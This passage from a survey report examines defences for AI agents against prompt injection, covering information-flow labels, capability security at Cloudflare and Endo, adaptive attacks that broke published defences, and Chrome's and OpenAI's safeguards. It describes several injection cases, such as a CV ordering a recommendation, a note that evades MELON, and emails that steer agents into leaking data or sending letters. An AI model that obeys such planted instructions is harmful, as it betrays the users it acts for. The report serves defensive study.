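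The team ran 6,600 test episodes with three models on a public benchmark of 24 tasks and their own set of 20 office scenarios. No attack succeeded in the 1,320 episodes with APPA's protection, and the agents completed between 64.2% and 91% of the tasks, depending on the model and the test. The team left out AgentDojo partly because recent models resist its standard attacks without any defence.

On the office scenarios, APPA completed 87% to 91% of tasks, while two versions of FIDES completed 36% to 46% and let 26% to 35% of attacks through. Kravchenko and colleagues set up both versions themselves, using Microsoft's framework, and acknowledge that the FIDES policies didn't include several rules the scenarios tested, such as sending something exactly once. The results therefore aren't a fair measure of FIDES in general. On the public benchmark, with one model and ordinary prompts, one FIDES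 version completed more tasks than APPA.

The comparison of APPA with reduced versions of itself is more convincing. With GPT-5.6 Luna, the full system completed 88% of the office tasks. It completed 56.5% without child branches and 35% without the suggested remedies. No attacks succeeded against any of these versions, so in these tests the full system completed more tasks without becoming less secure.

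All these designs assume that everything a model reads may influence everything it writes. *GIF* (Štorek, Holzer and colleagues, 2026) tries to measure the influence instead. In its main example, a company's agent screens job applicants and should recommend only people with five years of experience in Python and machine learning. An applicant with much less experience adds to his CV an instruction to recommend him at a salary of $200,000, and the agent obeys. GIF estimates that 82 bits of information flowed from the injected instruction into the recommendation, compared with 27 from the company's criteria and 16 from the rest of the text. A policy could block the recommendation because untrusted text influenced it most.

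To get such a number, GIF uses the fact that a model turns words into lists of numbers before processing them. It measures how much the model's next word, Y, would reveal about small random changes, U, to the numbers for one stretch of text. This quantity is the mutual information I(U; Y), which is zero if the changes make no difference to the next word.

Calculating it exactly is impractical for a large model, so the team uses an approximation based on M, a matrix that describes how strongly each small change shifts the probabilities of the next word. For changes of size τ, the estimate is

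GIF = ½ log det(I + τM),

where I is the identity matrix. The team proved, with every step checked in the proof language Lean, that

I(U; Y) ≤ GIF + o(τ),

where o(τ) is an error that shrinks faster than τ does. So for small enough changes, GIF doesn't significantly underestimate the flow.

The proof assumes that the model behaves smoothly near the text in question, and it covers only tiny changes to the numbers. Removing or replacing the applicant's instruction is a larger change, so the proof can't guarantee that a passage with a low score had no real effect on the agent's decision.

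The experiments suggest that the measure is useful anyway. In tests on six open models and three benchmarks, including AgentDojo, GIF flagged nearly all the harmful flows. When it picked out passages for a small model, Qwen 3 8B, to judge, the two together were about as accurate as GPT-5.5 with its reasoning set very high, and cost up to 81 times less. GIF needs access to a model's internal calculations, which companies such as OpenAI don't provide, but scores from a small open model also worked for models up to 200 times larger.

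A developer who uses GIF still has to decide how many bits are too many, and an attack that stays below that limit will get through. Conservative labels don't have this weakness, but they would also block a recommendation based on an honest CV.

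## Capability security: from a specialist community to Cloudflare's agent platform

Capability security limits what an agent can reach, whereas information-flow labels restrict what it does with data it has already read. Specialists in capability security are few and mostly know each other, so it is fairly easy to trace how their ideas got into an AI product. They got there mainly through Kenton Varda, an engineer at Cloudflare, which protects websites and runs its customers' code in data centres around the world.

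Varda posts on Friam, a mailing list tied to a Friday meeting of capability specialists, including Mark Miller. In September 2025 Alan Karp asked the list how to answer people who say that somebody would be using capabilities if they were so great. Varda replied in the thread, *Capabilities in production systems* (Karp, 2025), that Cloudflare Workers, the company's service for running code, used capabilities "because I designed it that way". He added that parts of Android and Chrome are capability systems too, though they aren't always called that. He rarely uses the term "object capability" in public because too few people know it.

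### Sandstorm, and why it found no market

Varda worked at Google for seven and a half years. According to his opensource.com profile, *Kenton Varda*, he was best known at Google for releasing Protocol Buffers, its format for exchanging data between programs, as open source. He then created Cap'n Proto, which lets one program call functions in another over a network. A Cap'n Proto message can carry a reference to an object, and whoever receives the reference can use the object. The developers of his next project, Sandstorm, wrote that this design came largely from the network protocol of Miller's language E.

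Varda announced Sandstorm in March 2014, as LWN reported. It was meant to let ordinary people run web apps on their own servers. Most web apps keep everyone's documents in one database and rely on the app's code to decide who sees what. Sandstorm instead ran each document in its own container, called a grain. Two documents in Etherpad, a shared text editor, ran in separate copies of the app with separate storage. Sandstorm controlled who could open each grain, so a bug in Etherpad couldn't expose a document to someone without access to it.

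A grain could contact the outside world only through Sandstorm. For example, a forum app might need to email users when someone replied to them. Normally the app would get the password to a mail server, which would also let it send spam to anyone. In Sandstorm, the app requested an object that accepts email, and Sandstorm showed the user a list of their own addresses. When the user picked one, the app received a capability to email only that address.

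Sandstorm called this list the Powerbox. It works like the window that opens when someone uploads a file to a website, where choosing the file also gives the website permission to read it. The user doesn't have to grant permission in a separate step, so the Powerbox comes close to what Saltzer and Schroeder meant by psychological acceptability.

The project attracted volunteers and ran on thousands of servers, but it had hardly any customers. When the money ran out, Varda (2017) blamed an alpha-quality product and the difficulty of selling to large companies. Hundreds of organisations had tried the paid version, but Varda (2024) later put the total at two sales, worth four figures. Investors had turned down a new funding round in 2016, and he wrote that he would never really know why.

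These are mostly business problems, so Sandstorm's failure is weak evidence against capability security. It does suggest that better security wasn't enough to sell a rough product. Varda has since said that the design also had technical problems, because a container for every document started too slowly and used too much memory.

Several companies wanted Sandstorm's engineers but would pay nothing for the company. One was Cloudflare, which already used Cap'n Proto heavily, as Varda (2017) wrote in *The Sandstorm Team is joining Cloudflare*. Cloudflare also offered him the project of working out how customers could run code in its data centres. His solution became Workers, which launched a year after he arrived.

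### Isolates and bindings

Workers runs each customer's code in an isolate, a separate instance of V8, the JavaScript engine in Google Chrome. Code in one isolate can't read another's memory. An isolate starts in a few milliseconds and needs a few megabytes of memory, while a container typically takes hundreds of milliseconds and hundreds of megabytes. Isolates removed much of the overhead that had hurt Sandstorm.

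The code gets access to other resources through bindings, which are live objects that the developer attaches to the program when deploying it. Cloudflare's description of the system's security gives the example of file storage, which Workers didn't offer. If Workers ever did, the program would receive an object for its own private directory and would have no way to name anyone else's.

Bindings also prevent a common attack on web servers that is closely related to the confused deputy. An attacker submits an address inside a company's private network, and the company's server, which has access the attacker lacks, fetches it. In 2024 Cloudflare argued that Workers are immune to this attack if developers use bindings properly, because the program reaches internal services through objects it already holds and an address supplied by an attacker can't be used to reach them.

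That article presented bindings as both more secure and more convenient for developers. In September 2025 Cloudflare began making the same case for AI agents. On the 22nd it released *Cap'n Web* (Cloudflare, 2025), an object-capability protocol for web browsers and servers. In a Friam thread about it, *capnweb* (Nagra, 2025), Varda wrote that Cloudflare would soon pitch capabilities as "the correct way to handle sandboxing AI".

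Four days later Varda announced that a Worker could now start a sandbox and run any code in it. In *Sandboxing in Cloudflare Workers* (Varda, 2025), he told the list that more and more people were realising capabilities were "the right model for AI agents and AI-generated code". He gave no examples and had a product to promote, so his claim is better evidence of his own plans than of a wider trend.

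### Code Mode's two motives

The product was Code Mode, in which the model writes a short program to make its tool calls instead of making them one at a time. Cloudflare's software reads the tool descriptions from each MCP service and turns them into functions in TypeScript, a version of JavaScript with types. The model then has a single tool, which runs code.

Varda and Pai begin *Code Mode* with efficiency. They argue that models handle complicated tools better when the tools are presented as code, because models have seen huge amounts of real code in training but only a small set of artificial tool calls. With ordinary tool calls, a result also has to pass through the model before it can go into the next call, even if the model only copies it. A program can pass the result along directly, which saves time and tokens. Cloudflare later reported that converting tools to code cut token use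 by up to 81%.

These savings don't depend on capabilities, since a developer would get them by running the same program in a sandbox with full internet access. The security argument comes later in the article, after Varda and Pai explain that generated code needs somewhere safe to run.

The two motives do help each other. Sandstorm had trouble selling security, but a developer who adopts Code Mode to reduce a bill also gets an isolated sandbox. Code Mode can also keep some hostile text away from the model. If a program searches a thousand chat messages and returns only Alice's, the model never reads the others. However, this protection is a side effect of how the program is written. A Code Mode program can print anything it has read, and the model will then read it too, whereas FIDES hides text according to its label.

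### Handing over an object instead of filtering traffic

Cloudflare made the sandbox available to all paying Workers customers in March 2026, as an open beta called Dynamic Workers. For the mail assistant from the start of this report, a developer could load the model's program roughly like this:

```
env.LOADER.load({
  mainModule: "task.js",
  modules: { "task.js": generatedCode },
  env: { THREAD: replyOnly },
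  globalOutbound: null
})
```

The developer has written `replyOnly`, an object with one function that takes the text of a reply. The generated program can call `env.THREAD.reply("Tuesday works")`, which sends a message out of the isolate to the developer's code. That code adds the recipient and the mail password and sends the email. The program can't write to a different address, because the function doesn't accept one. The last line blocks the program's internet access. Access is on unless the developer includes that line, so in this respect Dynamic Workers don't follow the principle of fail-safe defaults.

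On most platforms, by contrast, the program starts with general network access and a secret key for each service, and a filter inspects its traffic. Varda, Pai and Gupta explain in *Sandboxing AI agents, 100x faster* that such filters are hard to write because they have to understand what every request would do, and a request has many headers and parameters that could matter. The model also has to predict what the filter will block.

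For example, suppose an agent should only comment on one GitHub issue. A filter that allows traffic to GitHub also lets the agent publish private files to an attacker's GitHub repository. To prevent this, the filter has to check the path and often the body of each request, and its author has to update it when GitHub changes its interface. With a binding, the developer writes a function that comments on that issue. The agent can then do only what the developer has written a function for, whereas a filter lets through any request its author forgot to block.

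The binding also keeps the secret key out of the sandbox. Varda and Pai write that the AI therefore "cannot possibly write code that leaks any keys". The claim is fair for keys but doesn't extend to data. A program with one binding that reads customer records and another that posts to a public channel can still copy the records to the channel.

Cloudflare also supports filtering for agents that have to use an existing web interface. The filter can add the key to a request after it leaves the sandbox, so these agents don't need to hold the key either.

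The security of this design depends on the isolate, and Varda and colleagues acknowledge that security bugs are more common in V8 than in the software that separates virtual machines. Cloudflare adds a second sandbox around the isolates and installs V8's security fixes within hours, but a developer who runs the open-source version alone doesn't get these protections. The model should also write JavaScript, since Python works but loads and runs more slowly. The choice of language probably matters less when a model writes the code than when a programmer does.

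### Cloudflare OS and its Gatekeepers

Requests from Cloudflare's own staff gave it a reason to go further. In *How we're rethinking work at Cloudflare with Cloudflare OS*, Rhea, Cloudflare's chief information officer, describes a salesperson who had used AI to build a "SuperApp" and wanted access keys for about a dozen internal systems. Many others soon made similar requests. In May 2026 the company gave all its employees an agent that ran in a browser and reached company data through MCP.

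That first version tracked which tools an agent could call, but not which documents or tables the agent had read. When an employee shared the agent's work, a colleague might therefore learn something they weren't allowed to know. Cloudflare rebuilt the system and released the new version as open source in August 2026, which SiliconANGLE (2026) covered on the 5th.

Varda led the work and considers it Sandstorm's successor. As in Sandstorm, each document or small app runs separately, but in an isolate instead of a container. In a post that InfoQ's *Cloudflare OS* quotes, he argues that a company can therefore let people with no technical training build apps with AI while its security team can "sleep soundly at night". If the AI writes an app with a security bug, the platform still controls who can open it.

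In *Cloudflare OS*, Jones and Carter describe an agent that starts with no access and asks for a specific resource, such as one project's list of bugs. If the user agrees, the agent's code receives a binding for that resource. The binding goes through a Gatekeeper, a program written for one outside service. The Gatekeeper holds the password or key and can apply rules that the service may not offer. A Gatekeeper for GitHub could let an agent read the issues in one repository but not the code, hide certain fields, and require a person's approval before the agent merges a change.

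According to Varda, an agent doesn't have to wait for each approval. The Gatekeeper simulates the result so that the agent can carry on, and the user reviews the queued actions together at the end. This should reduce interruptions, but a long list might also tempt people to approve everything at once.

Cloudflare OS goes beyond Sandstorm by recording every resource the agent has read. Suppose Ann's agent reads a table of salaries and builds a chart from it, and Ann shares the chart with Ben. When Ben tries to open it, the Gatekeeper checks whether he has access to the salary table, and if he doesn't, he can't see the chart. Cloudflare OS can also use the record to restrict the agent after a sensitive read, by stopping it from writing to certain places, inviting new people, passing work to another agent or contacting the internet.

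This is information-flow control, although Jones and Carter don't use the term. The list of resources serves as a label that only grows, and the check on Ben has the same effect as the lists of readers in FIDES. Unlike FIDES, the Gatekeeper checks Ben's access when he opens the chart, so if he loses access to the table next month, he loses the chart too.

So the capability specialists' most complete product for agents also tracks data. It needs to, because bindings alone can't stop an agent from reading data through one binding and writing it through another. The drawback is label creep, so Ben can't open the chart even if it shows only the number of employees. Varda has called the current policies blunt and perhaps too restrictive.

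The isolation also has a gap in the browser. Jones and Carter write that neither an app's server code nor its browser code can reach the internet without a capability, but Varda has acknowledged that browsers' security rules can't block WebRTC, a technology for video calls that can also carry data. He therefore thinks the browser sandbox protects against an AI's mistakes but not against deliberately malicious code.

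The usage figures come from Cloudflare itself. Rhea reports that thousands of employees use the platform every week and that they made more than 4,000 apps and tools in 30 days. He estimates that the sales team saved over 10,000 hours in a month. These figures don't measure attacks or leaks. They also can't show how well people work under the new restrictions, because employees started on the first version, which had no Gatekeepers. Other companies can install the software themselves, and Cloudflare plans to offer a managed version.

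### Endo and hardened JavaScript

Miller and his colleagues instead worked on the JavaScript language itself. In ordinary JavaScript, all the code in a program shares built-in objects, such as the one that defines how lists work. A malicious library can change these objects and so affect code it has no reference to. This breaks Miller's rule that only connectivity begets connectivity.

Hardened JavaScript closes this route. It freezes the shared objects before other code runs, then lets a developer run each piece of code in a compartment that contains only the objects the developer puts there. Agoric, a company Miller helped found, uses it for programs that hold and trade digital money. MetaMask, a cryptocurrency wallet, uses it to confine plug-ins and outside libraries. Both had a strong reason to adopt this kind of security, since one bad library could immediately steal their users' money.

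The open-source project Endo grew out of this work, and Endo Familiar is its prototype for AI agents. The person and the agent exchange messages, which can carry capabilities. If the agent needs a folder, it asks for it, and the person can reply with a reference to that folder or refuse. This resembles Sandstorm's Powerbox, but uses a conversation instead of a list.

Endo Familiar and Cloudflare OS give agents access in much the same way, but they separate programs differently. Cloudflare puts each program in its own isolate and passes messages between them, while Endo's hardened JavaScript can also separate programs that share the same memory. Both enforce their limits as the program runs, whereas a 2026 design for the language Scala tracks capabilities in the program's types. In the thread Nagra started, Kris Kowal, who works on Endo, wrote that Cap'n Web's data format was nearly compatible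 with the one his group was developing and that the two might converge. Endo Familiar is still a prototype, while Cloudflare already has a platform and paying customers.

### How "confused deputy" entered standards and guidance

Hardy's phrase is more widely used than his remedy. Amazon already used it for a problem between customers' cloud accounts. A company may give an outside service, such as a cost-monitoring tool, access to its Amazon account. Another customer of that service could then enter the company's account details and have the service fetch the company's data. Amazon's fix is an extra identifier that the company and the service's provider agree on beforehand, as John Kemp explained on a capability mailing list in *Relevant to the recent thread* (Karp, 2025).

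The MCP specification's security guidance has a section on the "confused deputy problem" in logins. Some MCP servers connect agents to another company's service, such as a file store, and use one fixed identity there for all their clients. An attacker can register their own program with the MCP server and send a link to a user who has already approved that identity. The user's browser has stored that approval, so the file store skips the permission screen and the attacker's program receives the login code. The specification requires these servers to get the user's consent for each client program separately.

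That attack doesn't involve a language model, so an MCP server can follow the rule perfectly and still serve an agent that obeys instructions in a stranger's email. Adam Shostack wrote on the security blog Shostack + Friends that MCP had "all sorts of authentication and confused deputy problems", although he didn't consider them quite built in.

In December 2025 the UK's National Cyber Security Centre applied the phrase to the model itself. Its post *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* called language models "inherently confusable deputies", according to TinyFish, a company that builds web agents. This goes beyond Hardy's original point, which concerned a compiler that Tymshare could have repaired by changing how it received permissions. The centre doubts that anyone can fully repair a language model, so it advises developers to limit the damage a confused model can do.

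Amazon adds an identifier, MCP adds a consent screen, and the centre recommends general limits. None of these three remedies is an object capability. Other words from the field have changed meaning too. *We have to be careful about our terms* (Karp, 2025) describes a webinar about AI agents in which "delegation" meant passing on a user's whole identity, whereas Karp uses it to mean passing on one specific permission. The speakers also recommended least privilege, but they meant the privileges of a whole user account.

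### Wrong grants, and bad uses of right ones

In July 2026 Karp asked Friam whether anyone had proved that a capability system can't have a confused deputy. The replies in *Confused deputy* (Karp, 2026) show that it can. William Leslie pointed out that a program can keep its capabilities in a table and let a client choose one by name. If Tymshare's compiler had held capabilities for both the statistics and billing files and looked them up by the name a customer typed, the customer could still have destroyed the billing records.

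Miller answered that a program is safe from this attack if the only way to tell it what to act on is to hand it a capability. He called this a severe restriction, which many normal programs don't meet even in a capability system, although most of them are safe for other reasons.

An agent can rarely meet Miller's condition, because its model chooses which capability to use based on text that an attacker may have written. Giving the agent fewer and narrower capabilities leaves the attacker fewer options, but the attacker can still influence which of the remaining capabilities the agent uses.

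People can also make mistakes when deciding what to grant. A user in a hurry may approve access to a whole GitHub account when one repository would do, and the isolate will then enforce that overly broad limit. InfoQ's editor similarly cautioned, in response to Varda's claims, that a company could misconfigure its Gatekeepers. Varda has said that AI can write most of a new Gatekeeper, which makes it quick to connect another service, but an error in a Gatekeeper affects every agent that uses it. Many developers don't set narrow limits at all, because common agent frameworks treat having a tool as permission for any use of it, as Mellafe Zuvic argues in *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* (2026).

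An agent can misuse permissions even when they were granted correctly. *Capabilities Can't See Your Agent's Objective* uses as its main example a 2025 incident in which a coding agent from Replit deleted a customer's live database. No attacker was involved, and the agent had valid credentials and permission to change the database. The essay acknowledges that these permissions were too broad, but points out that an agent sometimes needs broad permissions to do its job.

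A narrower capability might have helped here, such as one that let the agent add and edit records but not delete them, or one that saved a copy before each change. But if the user had asked the agent to clear out old records, the agent would have needed to delete some, and it couldn't have learned from the capability which ones the user wanted to keep.

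## October 2025 to March 2026: Google and OpenAI add limits outside the model

CaMeL and FIDES limit what can happen when a model obeys an attacker. Simpler defences use prompts, extra training or filters to try to stop the model from obeying, and papers on them often reported that almost no attacks succeeded. In October 2025, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues tested 12 of these defences in *The Attacker Moves Second* and broke all of them, with attack success rates above 90% for most.

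The 14 researchers came from OpenAI, Anthropic, Google DeepMind, ETH Zurich, Northeastern University, the research programme MATS, the AI Sequrity Company and HackAPrompt, which runs competitions in attacking language models. Five of them had helped build CaMeL. Another, Chawin Sitawarin, had helped build StruQ, one of the 12 defences.

Earlier tests had mostly replayed a fixed list of old attacks, but Nasr and colleagues let the attacker adapt to each defence. Their attacks repeatedly proposed some text, tried it on the defended model, scored the result and used the best attempts to write the next batch. They did this in four ways. The first used the model's internal calculations to choose words, the second trained an attacking model by reinforcement learning, and the third had a model keep mutating the most successful attacks. The fourth was a competition with over 500 human participants.

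| Defence | How it tries to stop prompt injection | Adaptive attacks that succeeded |
|---|---|---|
| Spotlighting | Marks text so the model knows what to trust | Over 95% |
| Meta SecAlign | Trains the model on examples of attacks | 96% |
| Protect AI, PromptGuard, Model Armor | Use a separate model to detect attacks | Over 90% |
| PIGuard | Uses a separate model to detect attacks | 71% |
| MELON | Runs the agent twice and compares its tool calls | 76%, or 95% if the attacker knows the design |

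With AgentDojo's standard attacks, the success rate against spotlighting had been as low as 1%, and Meta SecAlign's developers had reported 2%.

MELON shows why a fixed test is misleading. It runs the agent a second time with the user's request replaced by a request to summarise the tools' results. If the same tool calls appear in both runs, they probably came from the data, so MELON blocks them. The attacker added a note telling any system that was only summarising the file to ignore the instructions above. The malicious tool calls then didn't appear in the second run, so MELON didn't block them.

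People were still the best attackers. On a selected set of scenarios, they eventually beat every defence, while the automated search succeeded 69% of the time.

The attackers had plenty of computing power, and when attacking a detector they could see the detector's confidence. The study therefore shows that someone can break these defences, but it doesn't measure how often criminals would make the effort. Nasr and colleagues still consider detectors useful against unsophisticated attacks. They didn't test any design like CaMeL, in which ordinary code enforces the limits.

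### How much better the models have become

Models have improved a lot since then. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) describes a competition that the security company Gray Swan ran with OpenAI, Anthropic, Meta, Amazon and the British and American government AI institutes. The 464 participants made about 272,000 attempts on 13 models and succeeded 8,648 times. Attacks succeeded against every model, at rates from 0.5% for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% for Gemini 2.5 Pro.

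In most scenarios, participants had to make the agent do something harmful and hide it from the user. In one, a marketing email gets an assistant to mark a message about a contract deadline as read and leave it out of its summary. Participants could read the conversation in advance and knew which tool call they needed, advantages that real attackers usually lack. Dziemian and colleagues therefore treat the rates as an upper bound for single-turn attacks.

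These rates are per attempt, and an attacker can try again. In another Gray Swan test, attacks on Opus 4.5 succeeded 4.7% of the time with one attempt, 33.6% with ten and 63% with a hundred, according to The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals*. Success rates also depend on the setting. According to VentureBeat, none of 200 attempts succeeded against Opus 4.6 in a restricted coding environment in February 2026. When the same model operated a graphical interface with its safeguards on, attackers succeeded 57.1% of the time by the 200th attempt.

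Later models resisted attacks much better. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser based prompt injection* gives an attack success rate of 2.0% for Opus 5 after 15 attempts on Gray Swan's general test, down from 5.5% for Opus 4.8. No attack succeeded in 129 browser scenarios. Robustness improved again with Fable 5.1, according to *Claude Fable 5.1 and Mythos 5.1*, a review of Anthropic's report on those models.

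Anthropic also paid an outside company, Trajectory Labs, to attack Claude Code in auto mode, in which the software decides whether to allow an action instead of asking the user. None of 720 attempts against three recent models succeeded. Willison discusses the result in *30 posts tagged “lethal-trifecta”* and wants more independent confirmation. He suggests an attack that might well work on a human developer too, in which a software package's instructions tell the agent to download some files with a particular tool before running the tests, and the tool secretly steals data.

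Nasr and colleagues argue that a defence isn't proven secure just because even a very good test fails to break it. Anderson made a similar point about tiger teams in 1972. Gray Swan now repeats its competition with new scenarios. The *Beam Model Technical Report* (2026), from November, describes a three-week contest with large prizes for attacks on production harnesses, so outside testers are starting to examine the software around the model as well as the model itself.

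### Two rules a developer can check on paper

Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, warned against combining three things in one agent: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to communicate with the outside world. An attacker can use prompt injection against an agent that has all three, by planting an instruction in the content to collect the private data and send it to the attacker. If any one of the three is missing, this theft isn't possible.

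The trifecta is a simplified information-flow rule. The same three ingredients are present when FIDES blocks a public comment after an agent has read a stranger's bug report and a private file. But FIDES checks what the agent has read by that point, while the trifecta depends only on what the agent could do. A developer can apply the trifecta without labels, but it also rules out a lot of harmless work, because the mail assistant has all three properties even on a day when no stranger writes to it.

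Willison wrote the rule partly for users who connect tools from different sources through MCP. Each tool may be reasonable by itself, but no vendor checks the combination. A single service can also supply all three capabilities, as GitHub's MCP server did in the attack on private repositories.

Meta, the owner of Facebook, made this into a design rule on 31 October 2025. Under Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025), an agent should have no more than two of these properties in one session:

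- A: it processes untrustworthy inputs.
- B: it has access to sensitive systems or private data.
- C: it can change something or communicate externally.

An agent that needs all three should be supervised, for example by a person who approves its actions. The name comes from a rule for Chromium, the open-source project behind Chrome, that code should not combine untrusted input, an unsafe programming language and high privileges.

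Meta gives three ways for a mail assistant to follow the rule. The assistant can read mail only from trusted senders (B and C), work in a test environment with no real data (A and C), or send mail only to trusted recipients or after a person has checked the draft (A and B). The last is probably the most useful, and it is very similar to a FIDES policy on who may receive a message.

An agent can also change its permissions during a session. It might research a question on the open web while it has no private data, then permanently lose the ability to communicate before it opens internal files. It has to lose that ability first because, if it has read a hostile page, the attacker's instructions may still be in its context. Information-flow systems handle this with a context label that can only become more restrictive.

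Meta's third property is broader than Willison's because it includes changing things as well as sending data. This led Willison to object, in an addition to his post on the rule, *New prompt injection papers*, that Meta's diagram marked the combination of A and C as safe even though an agent with no private data can still do damage. For example, if an agent reads strangers' comments and can edit a public wiki, a comment could make it delete pages. Meta changed the diagram. Meta also warns in its post that the rule doesn't cover an agent's own mistakes or a user who approves a warning without reading it.

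### Chrome's critic and its limits on websites

Chrome's agent works in the user's own browser, where the user may already be signed in to a bank, an email account and an employer's systems. A hijacked agent could use all of them, which makes this a serious case of ambient authority. *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025), published on 8 December 2025, describes Google's defences.

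When a user asks the agent to buy a T-shirt, a planning model based on Gemini reads the shop's page, including customer reviews, and proposes a step such as adding a shirt to the cart. Parker accepts that this model is inherently vulnerable, because anyone can write a review. Google uses spotlighting and trains the model on known attacks, but Nasr and colleagues had broken both kinds of defence two months earlier. Chrome therefore needs something else to catch the planner's mistakes.

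One such check is a second Gemini model, the User Alignment Critic, which reviews each step before Chrome carries it out. It receives a description of the proposed action but no unfiltered web content, and decides whether the action serves the user's goal. If it vetoes the step, the planner gets feedback and tries again. After repeated failures, the planner can hand control back to the user.

Parker credits the dual-LLM pattern and CaMeL as partial inspiration for Chrome's design. All three keep one model away from untrusted text. In CaMeL that model writes the whole plan, while in Chrome it only reviews steps chosen by a planner that has already read the page.

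| | CaMeL | Chrome's agent in December 2025 |
|---|---|---|
| What the planner reads | The user's request | The request and web pages |
| When it decides what to do | Before any model reads untrusted data | After each new page |
| What an injected instruction can do | Change values, or choose among branches already in the plan | Make the planner propose a new action |
| What checks an action | Policies written in code | A model, with coded checks for some actions |
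| What the system tracks | The source and permitted readers of every value | The websites on which the agent may act |

Google's choice helps with tasks that require reading a page before deciding what to click, such as shopping on an unfamiliar website. CaMeL does badly at these tasks. But Chrome loses CaMeL's main guarantee, that untrusted text can't add an action to the plan.

The critic should catch a bank transfer attempted during a T-shirt order. It will have more trouble with an attack that stays close to the task. If a seller's page leads the planner to pick an overpriced shirt, "add a T-shirt to the cart" still matches what the user wanted. Dziemian and colleagues chose harmful actions related to the agent's task, and many of those might look reasonable to a model that can't see the page. Parker acknowledges that the critic has less context but points out that its job is simpler.

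The other main defence extends a much older one. Browsers already stop the code on one website from reading most data belonging to another, and Chrome runs different sites in separate processes. These protections are based on origins, which roughly means individual websites. An agent that reads and clicks on many sites could carry data across the boundaries, so Parker's design gives each task two sets of origins. Let R be the sites the agent may only read, and W the sites it may both read and act on. Website data can then move only in this direction:

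R ∪ W → W.

For instance, a user might want the ingredients for a recipe delivered. The recipe site belongs in R and the supermarket in W. The user's bank belongs in neither, so if a comment under the recipe tells the agent to open the bank's site, Chrome should refuse. Chrome also hides embedded content from unrelated sites, such as advertisements. This would have hidden the fake cookie notice that Foerster and colleagues put in an advertisement to mislead CaMeL, if the advertisement came from a different site.

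The browser's code can enforce these sets whatever the planner outputs. But when the planner tries to visit a new site, a variant of the critic decides whether the site is relevant. Although that variant isn't given web content, it is a model and can be wrong.

Google's first release also left out part of the design. It tracked only W, with no separate set of sites that the agent could read but not act on. Without that set, Chrome has to either leave reading unrestricted or let the agent act on every site it reads, and both weaken the rule above. Parker explains that Google wanted to see how the limits affected real tasks before tuning them.

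Even the complete version wouldn't protect the mail assistant very well, because a webmail service has the stranger's message, the user's private mail and the send button all on the same site. Origin sets can't separate them, whereas FIDES could give each message its own label.

For such cases Chrome depends on the critic and on asking the user. It asks before the agent visits any site on a list of sensitive ones, including banks and medical services. It also asks before signing in with a saved password, which the model never sees. Parker says the agent "will try to pause" before making a purchase or sending a message, which is weaker than a coded rule.

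An Anthropic study published in August 2026 suggests that people are poor at this kind of check. Partway through a Claude Code session, the researchers replaced one permission request with a request to run a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6% of the 1,053 paid developers refused it, while auto mode would have blocked 89% of these commands. Anthropic was promoting auto mode at the time, and approving a coding command isn't the same as confirming a payment. Still, Saltzer and Schroeder's warning about interfaces that people use without thinking seems to apply.

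By August 2026 the critic was part of auto browse, Chrome's feature for automating tasks (Berschadski, 2026, *Future Mode Part 2*). Business customers could also apply their data-protection rules to agents, and an agent could reach only data that the employee using it was allowed to see. Chrome's history marked pages that an agent had visited. Berschadski again describes limiting the agent to relevant sites but doesn't mention separate permissions for reading and acting, so it is unclear whether Google has added the missing set.

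Google tests the agent with attacks by external researchers and automated systems, and pays up to $20,000 for a serious flaw. Neither post gives the share of attacks these defences stop, so we can't compare them with CaMeL's results.

### OpenAI's comparison with a customer-service worker

OpenAI's browser, ChatGPT Atlas, has a similar agent. In December 2025 OpenAI released an update with a model trained against an automated attacker. The Decoder's *OpenAI admits prompt injection may never be fully solved* reported that the attacker learned by reinforcement learning, one of the methods Nasr and colleagues had used. The attacker found, for example, an email that made the agent send a resignation letter to the user's boss when the user had asked for an out-of-office reply.

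OpenAI explained its wider approach in *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection*, published on 11 March 2026. It said the most effective attacks had begun to resemble social engineering, in which someone tricks a person into giving away information or access. The post's example, a friendly email about a company restructuring, worked half the time in testing. Among some ordinary tasks, the writer asks for an employee's name and address and adds that the assistant is fully authorised to submit them to a "compliance validation system".

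A filter would have trouble with this email because companies really do have systems like that, and it usually lacks the context needed to identify this one as fake. OpenAI compares the agent to a customer-service worker who can give refunds. Some customers will lie, and training the worker won't stop every lie from succeeding, so the employer also limits how much any worker can refund. OpenAI recommends asking what controls a person in the agent's position would have, and then building those.

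The Decoder had already objected in December, when OpenAI made a similar comparison between prompt injection and social engineering. Social engineering exploits people's trust, haste or inattention, and companies can train people to be more careful, but prompt injection comes from a technical flaw in the model. The Decoder argued that treating the two as similar makes the flaw seem more acceptable and shifts responsibility onto users.

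People and models fail in different ways. A worker who receives the same odd request a hundred times will probably tell a manager, but an attacker can keep testing messages on a model until one works. That message may also work elsewhere, since Dziemian and colleagues found attack strategies that transferred across 21 of their 41 scenarios and several model families.

OpenAI later described another difference in its August 2026 guide, *Agent security in the enterprise*. If an agent that pays invoices finds that a software subscription is about to expire, it might decide that renewing the subscription helps with its task and try to pay. An employee would recognise the renewal as a new contract and ask someone, while conventional software would stop because no rule covered it.

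The Decoder's objection is strongest against the idea that society can tolerate hijacked agents because it tolerates scams. It is a weak argument against limiting refunds, since a permanent flaw in the model, if anything, makes limits in the surrounding software more important.

### How Safe URL decides

OpenAI also uses source-sink analysis, which comes from the same tradition as Perl's taint mode. A source is a place where an attacker can influence the system, such as a web page. A sink is an action that becomes dangerous under that influence, such as sending data to someone else. An attacker needs both, so a developer who can't make every source safe can still limit attacks by controlling the sinks.

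A web address is an easily overlooked sink. Merely loading an address sends any private data in it to the website's owner, as in the image attack on the dual-LLM pattern.

OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) explains why a list of trusted websites isn't enough to protect users' data. A link to a trusted site may redirect to an untrusted one, and a short list produces so many warnings that users stop reading them. Willison's posts give two other examples of the problem. In November 2025, the security company PromptArmor found that the default list in Google's coding tool Antigravity included webhook.site, where anyone can create a page that records incoming requests. In January 2026, PromptArmor got Anthropic's Claude Cowork to upload a user's files through Anthropic's service, which was on the list, by supplying the attacker's access key.

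OpenAI's solution, Safe URL, checks the exact address instead of the site. OpenAI has a web crawler that records public addresses in an index and has no access to anyone's conversations. Before an agent automatically loads an address, Safe URL looks for it in that index. If the address is there, the agent can load it. Otherwise, the software either tells the agent to try another way or shows the user a warning and asks for permission.

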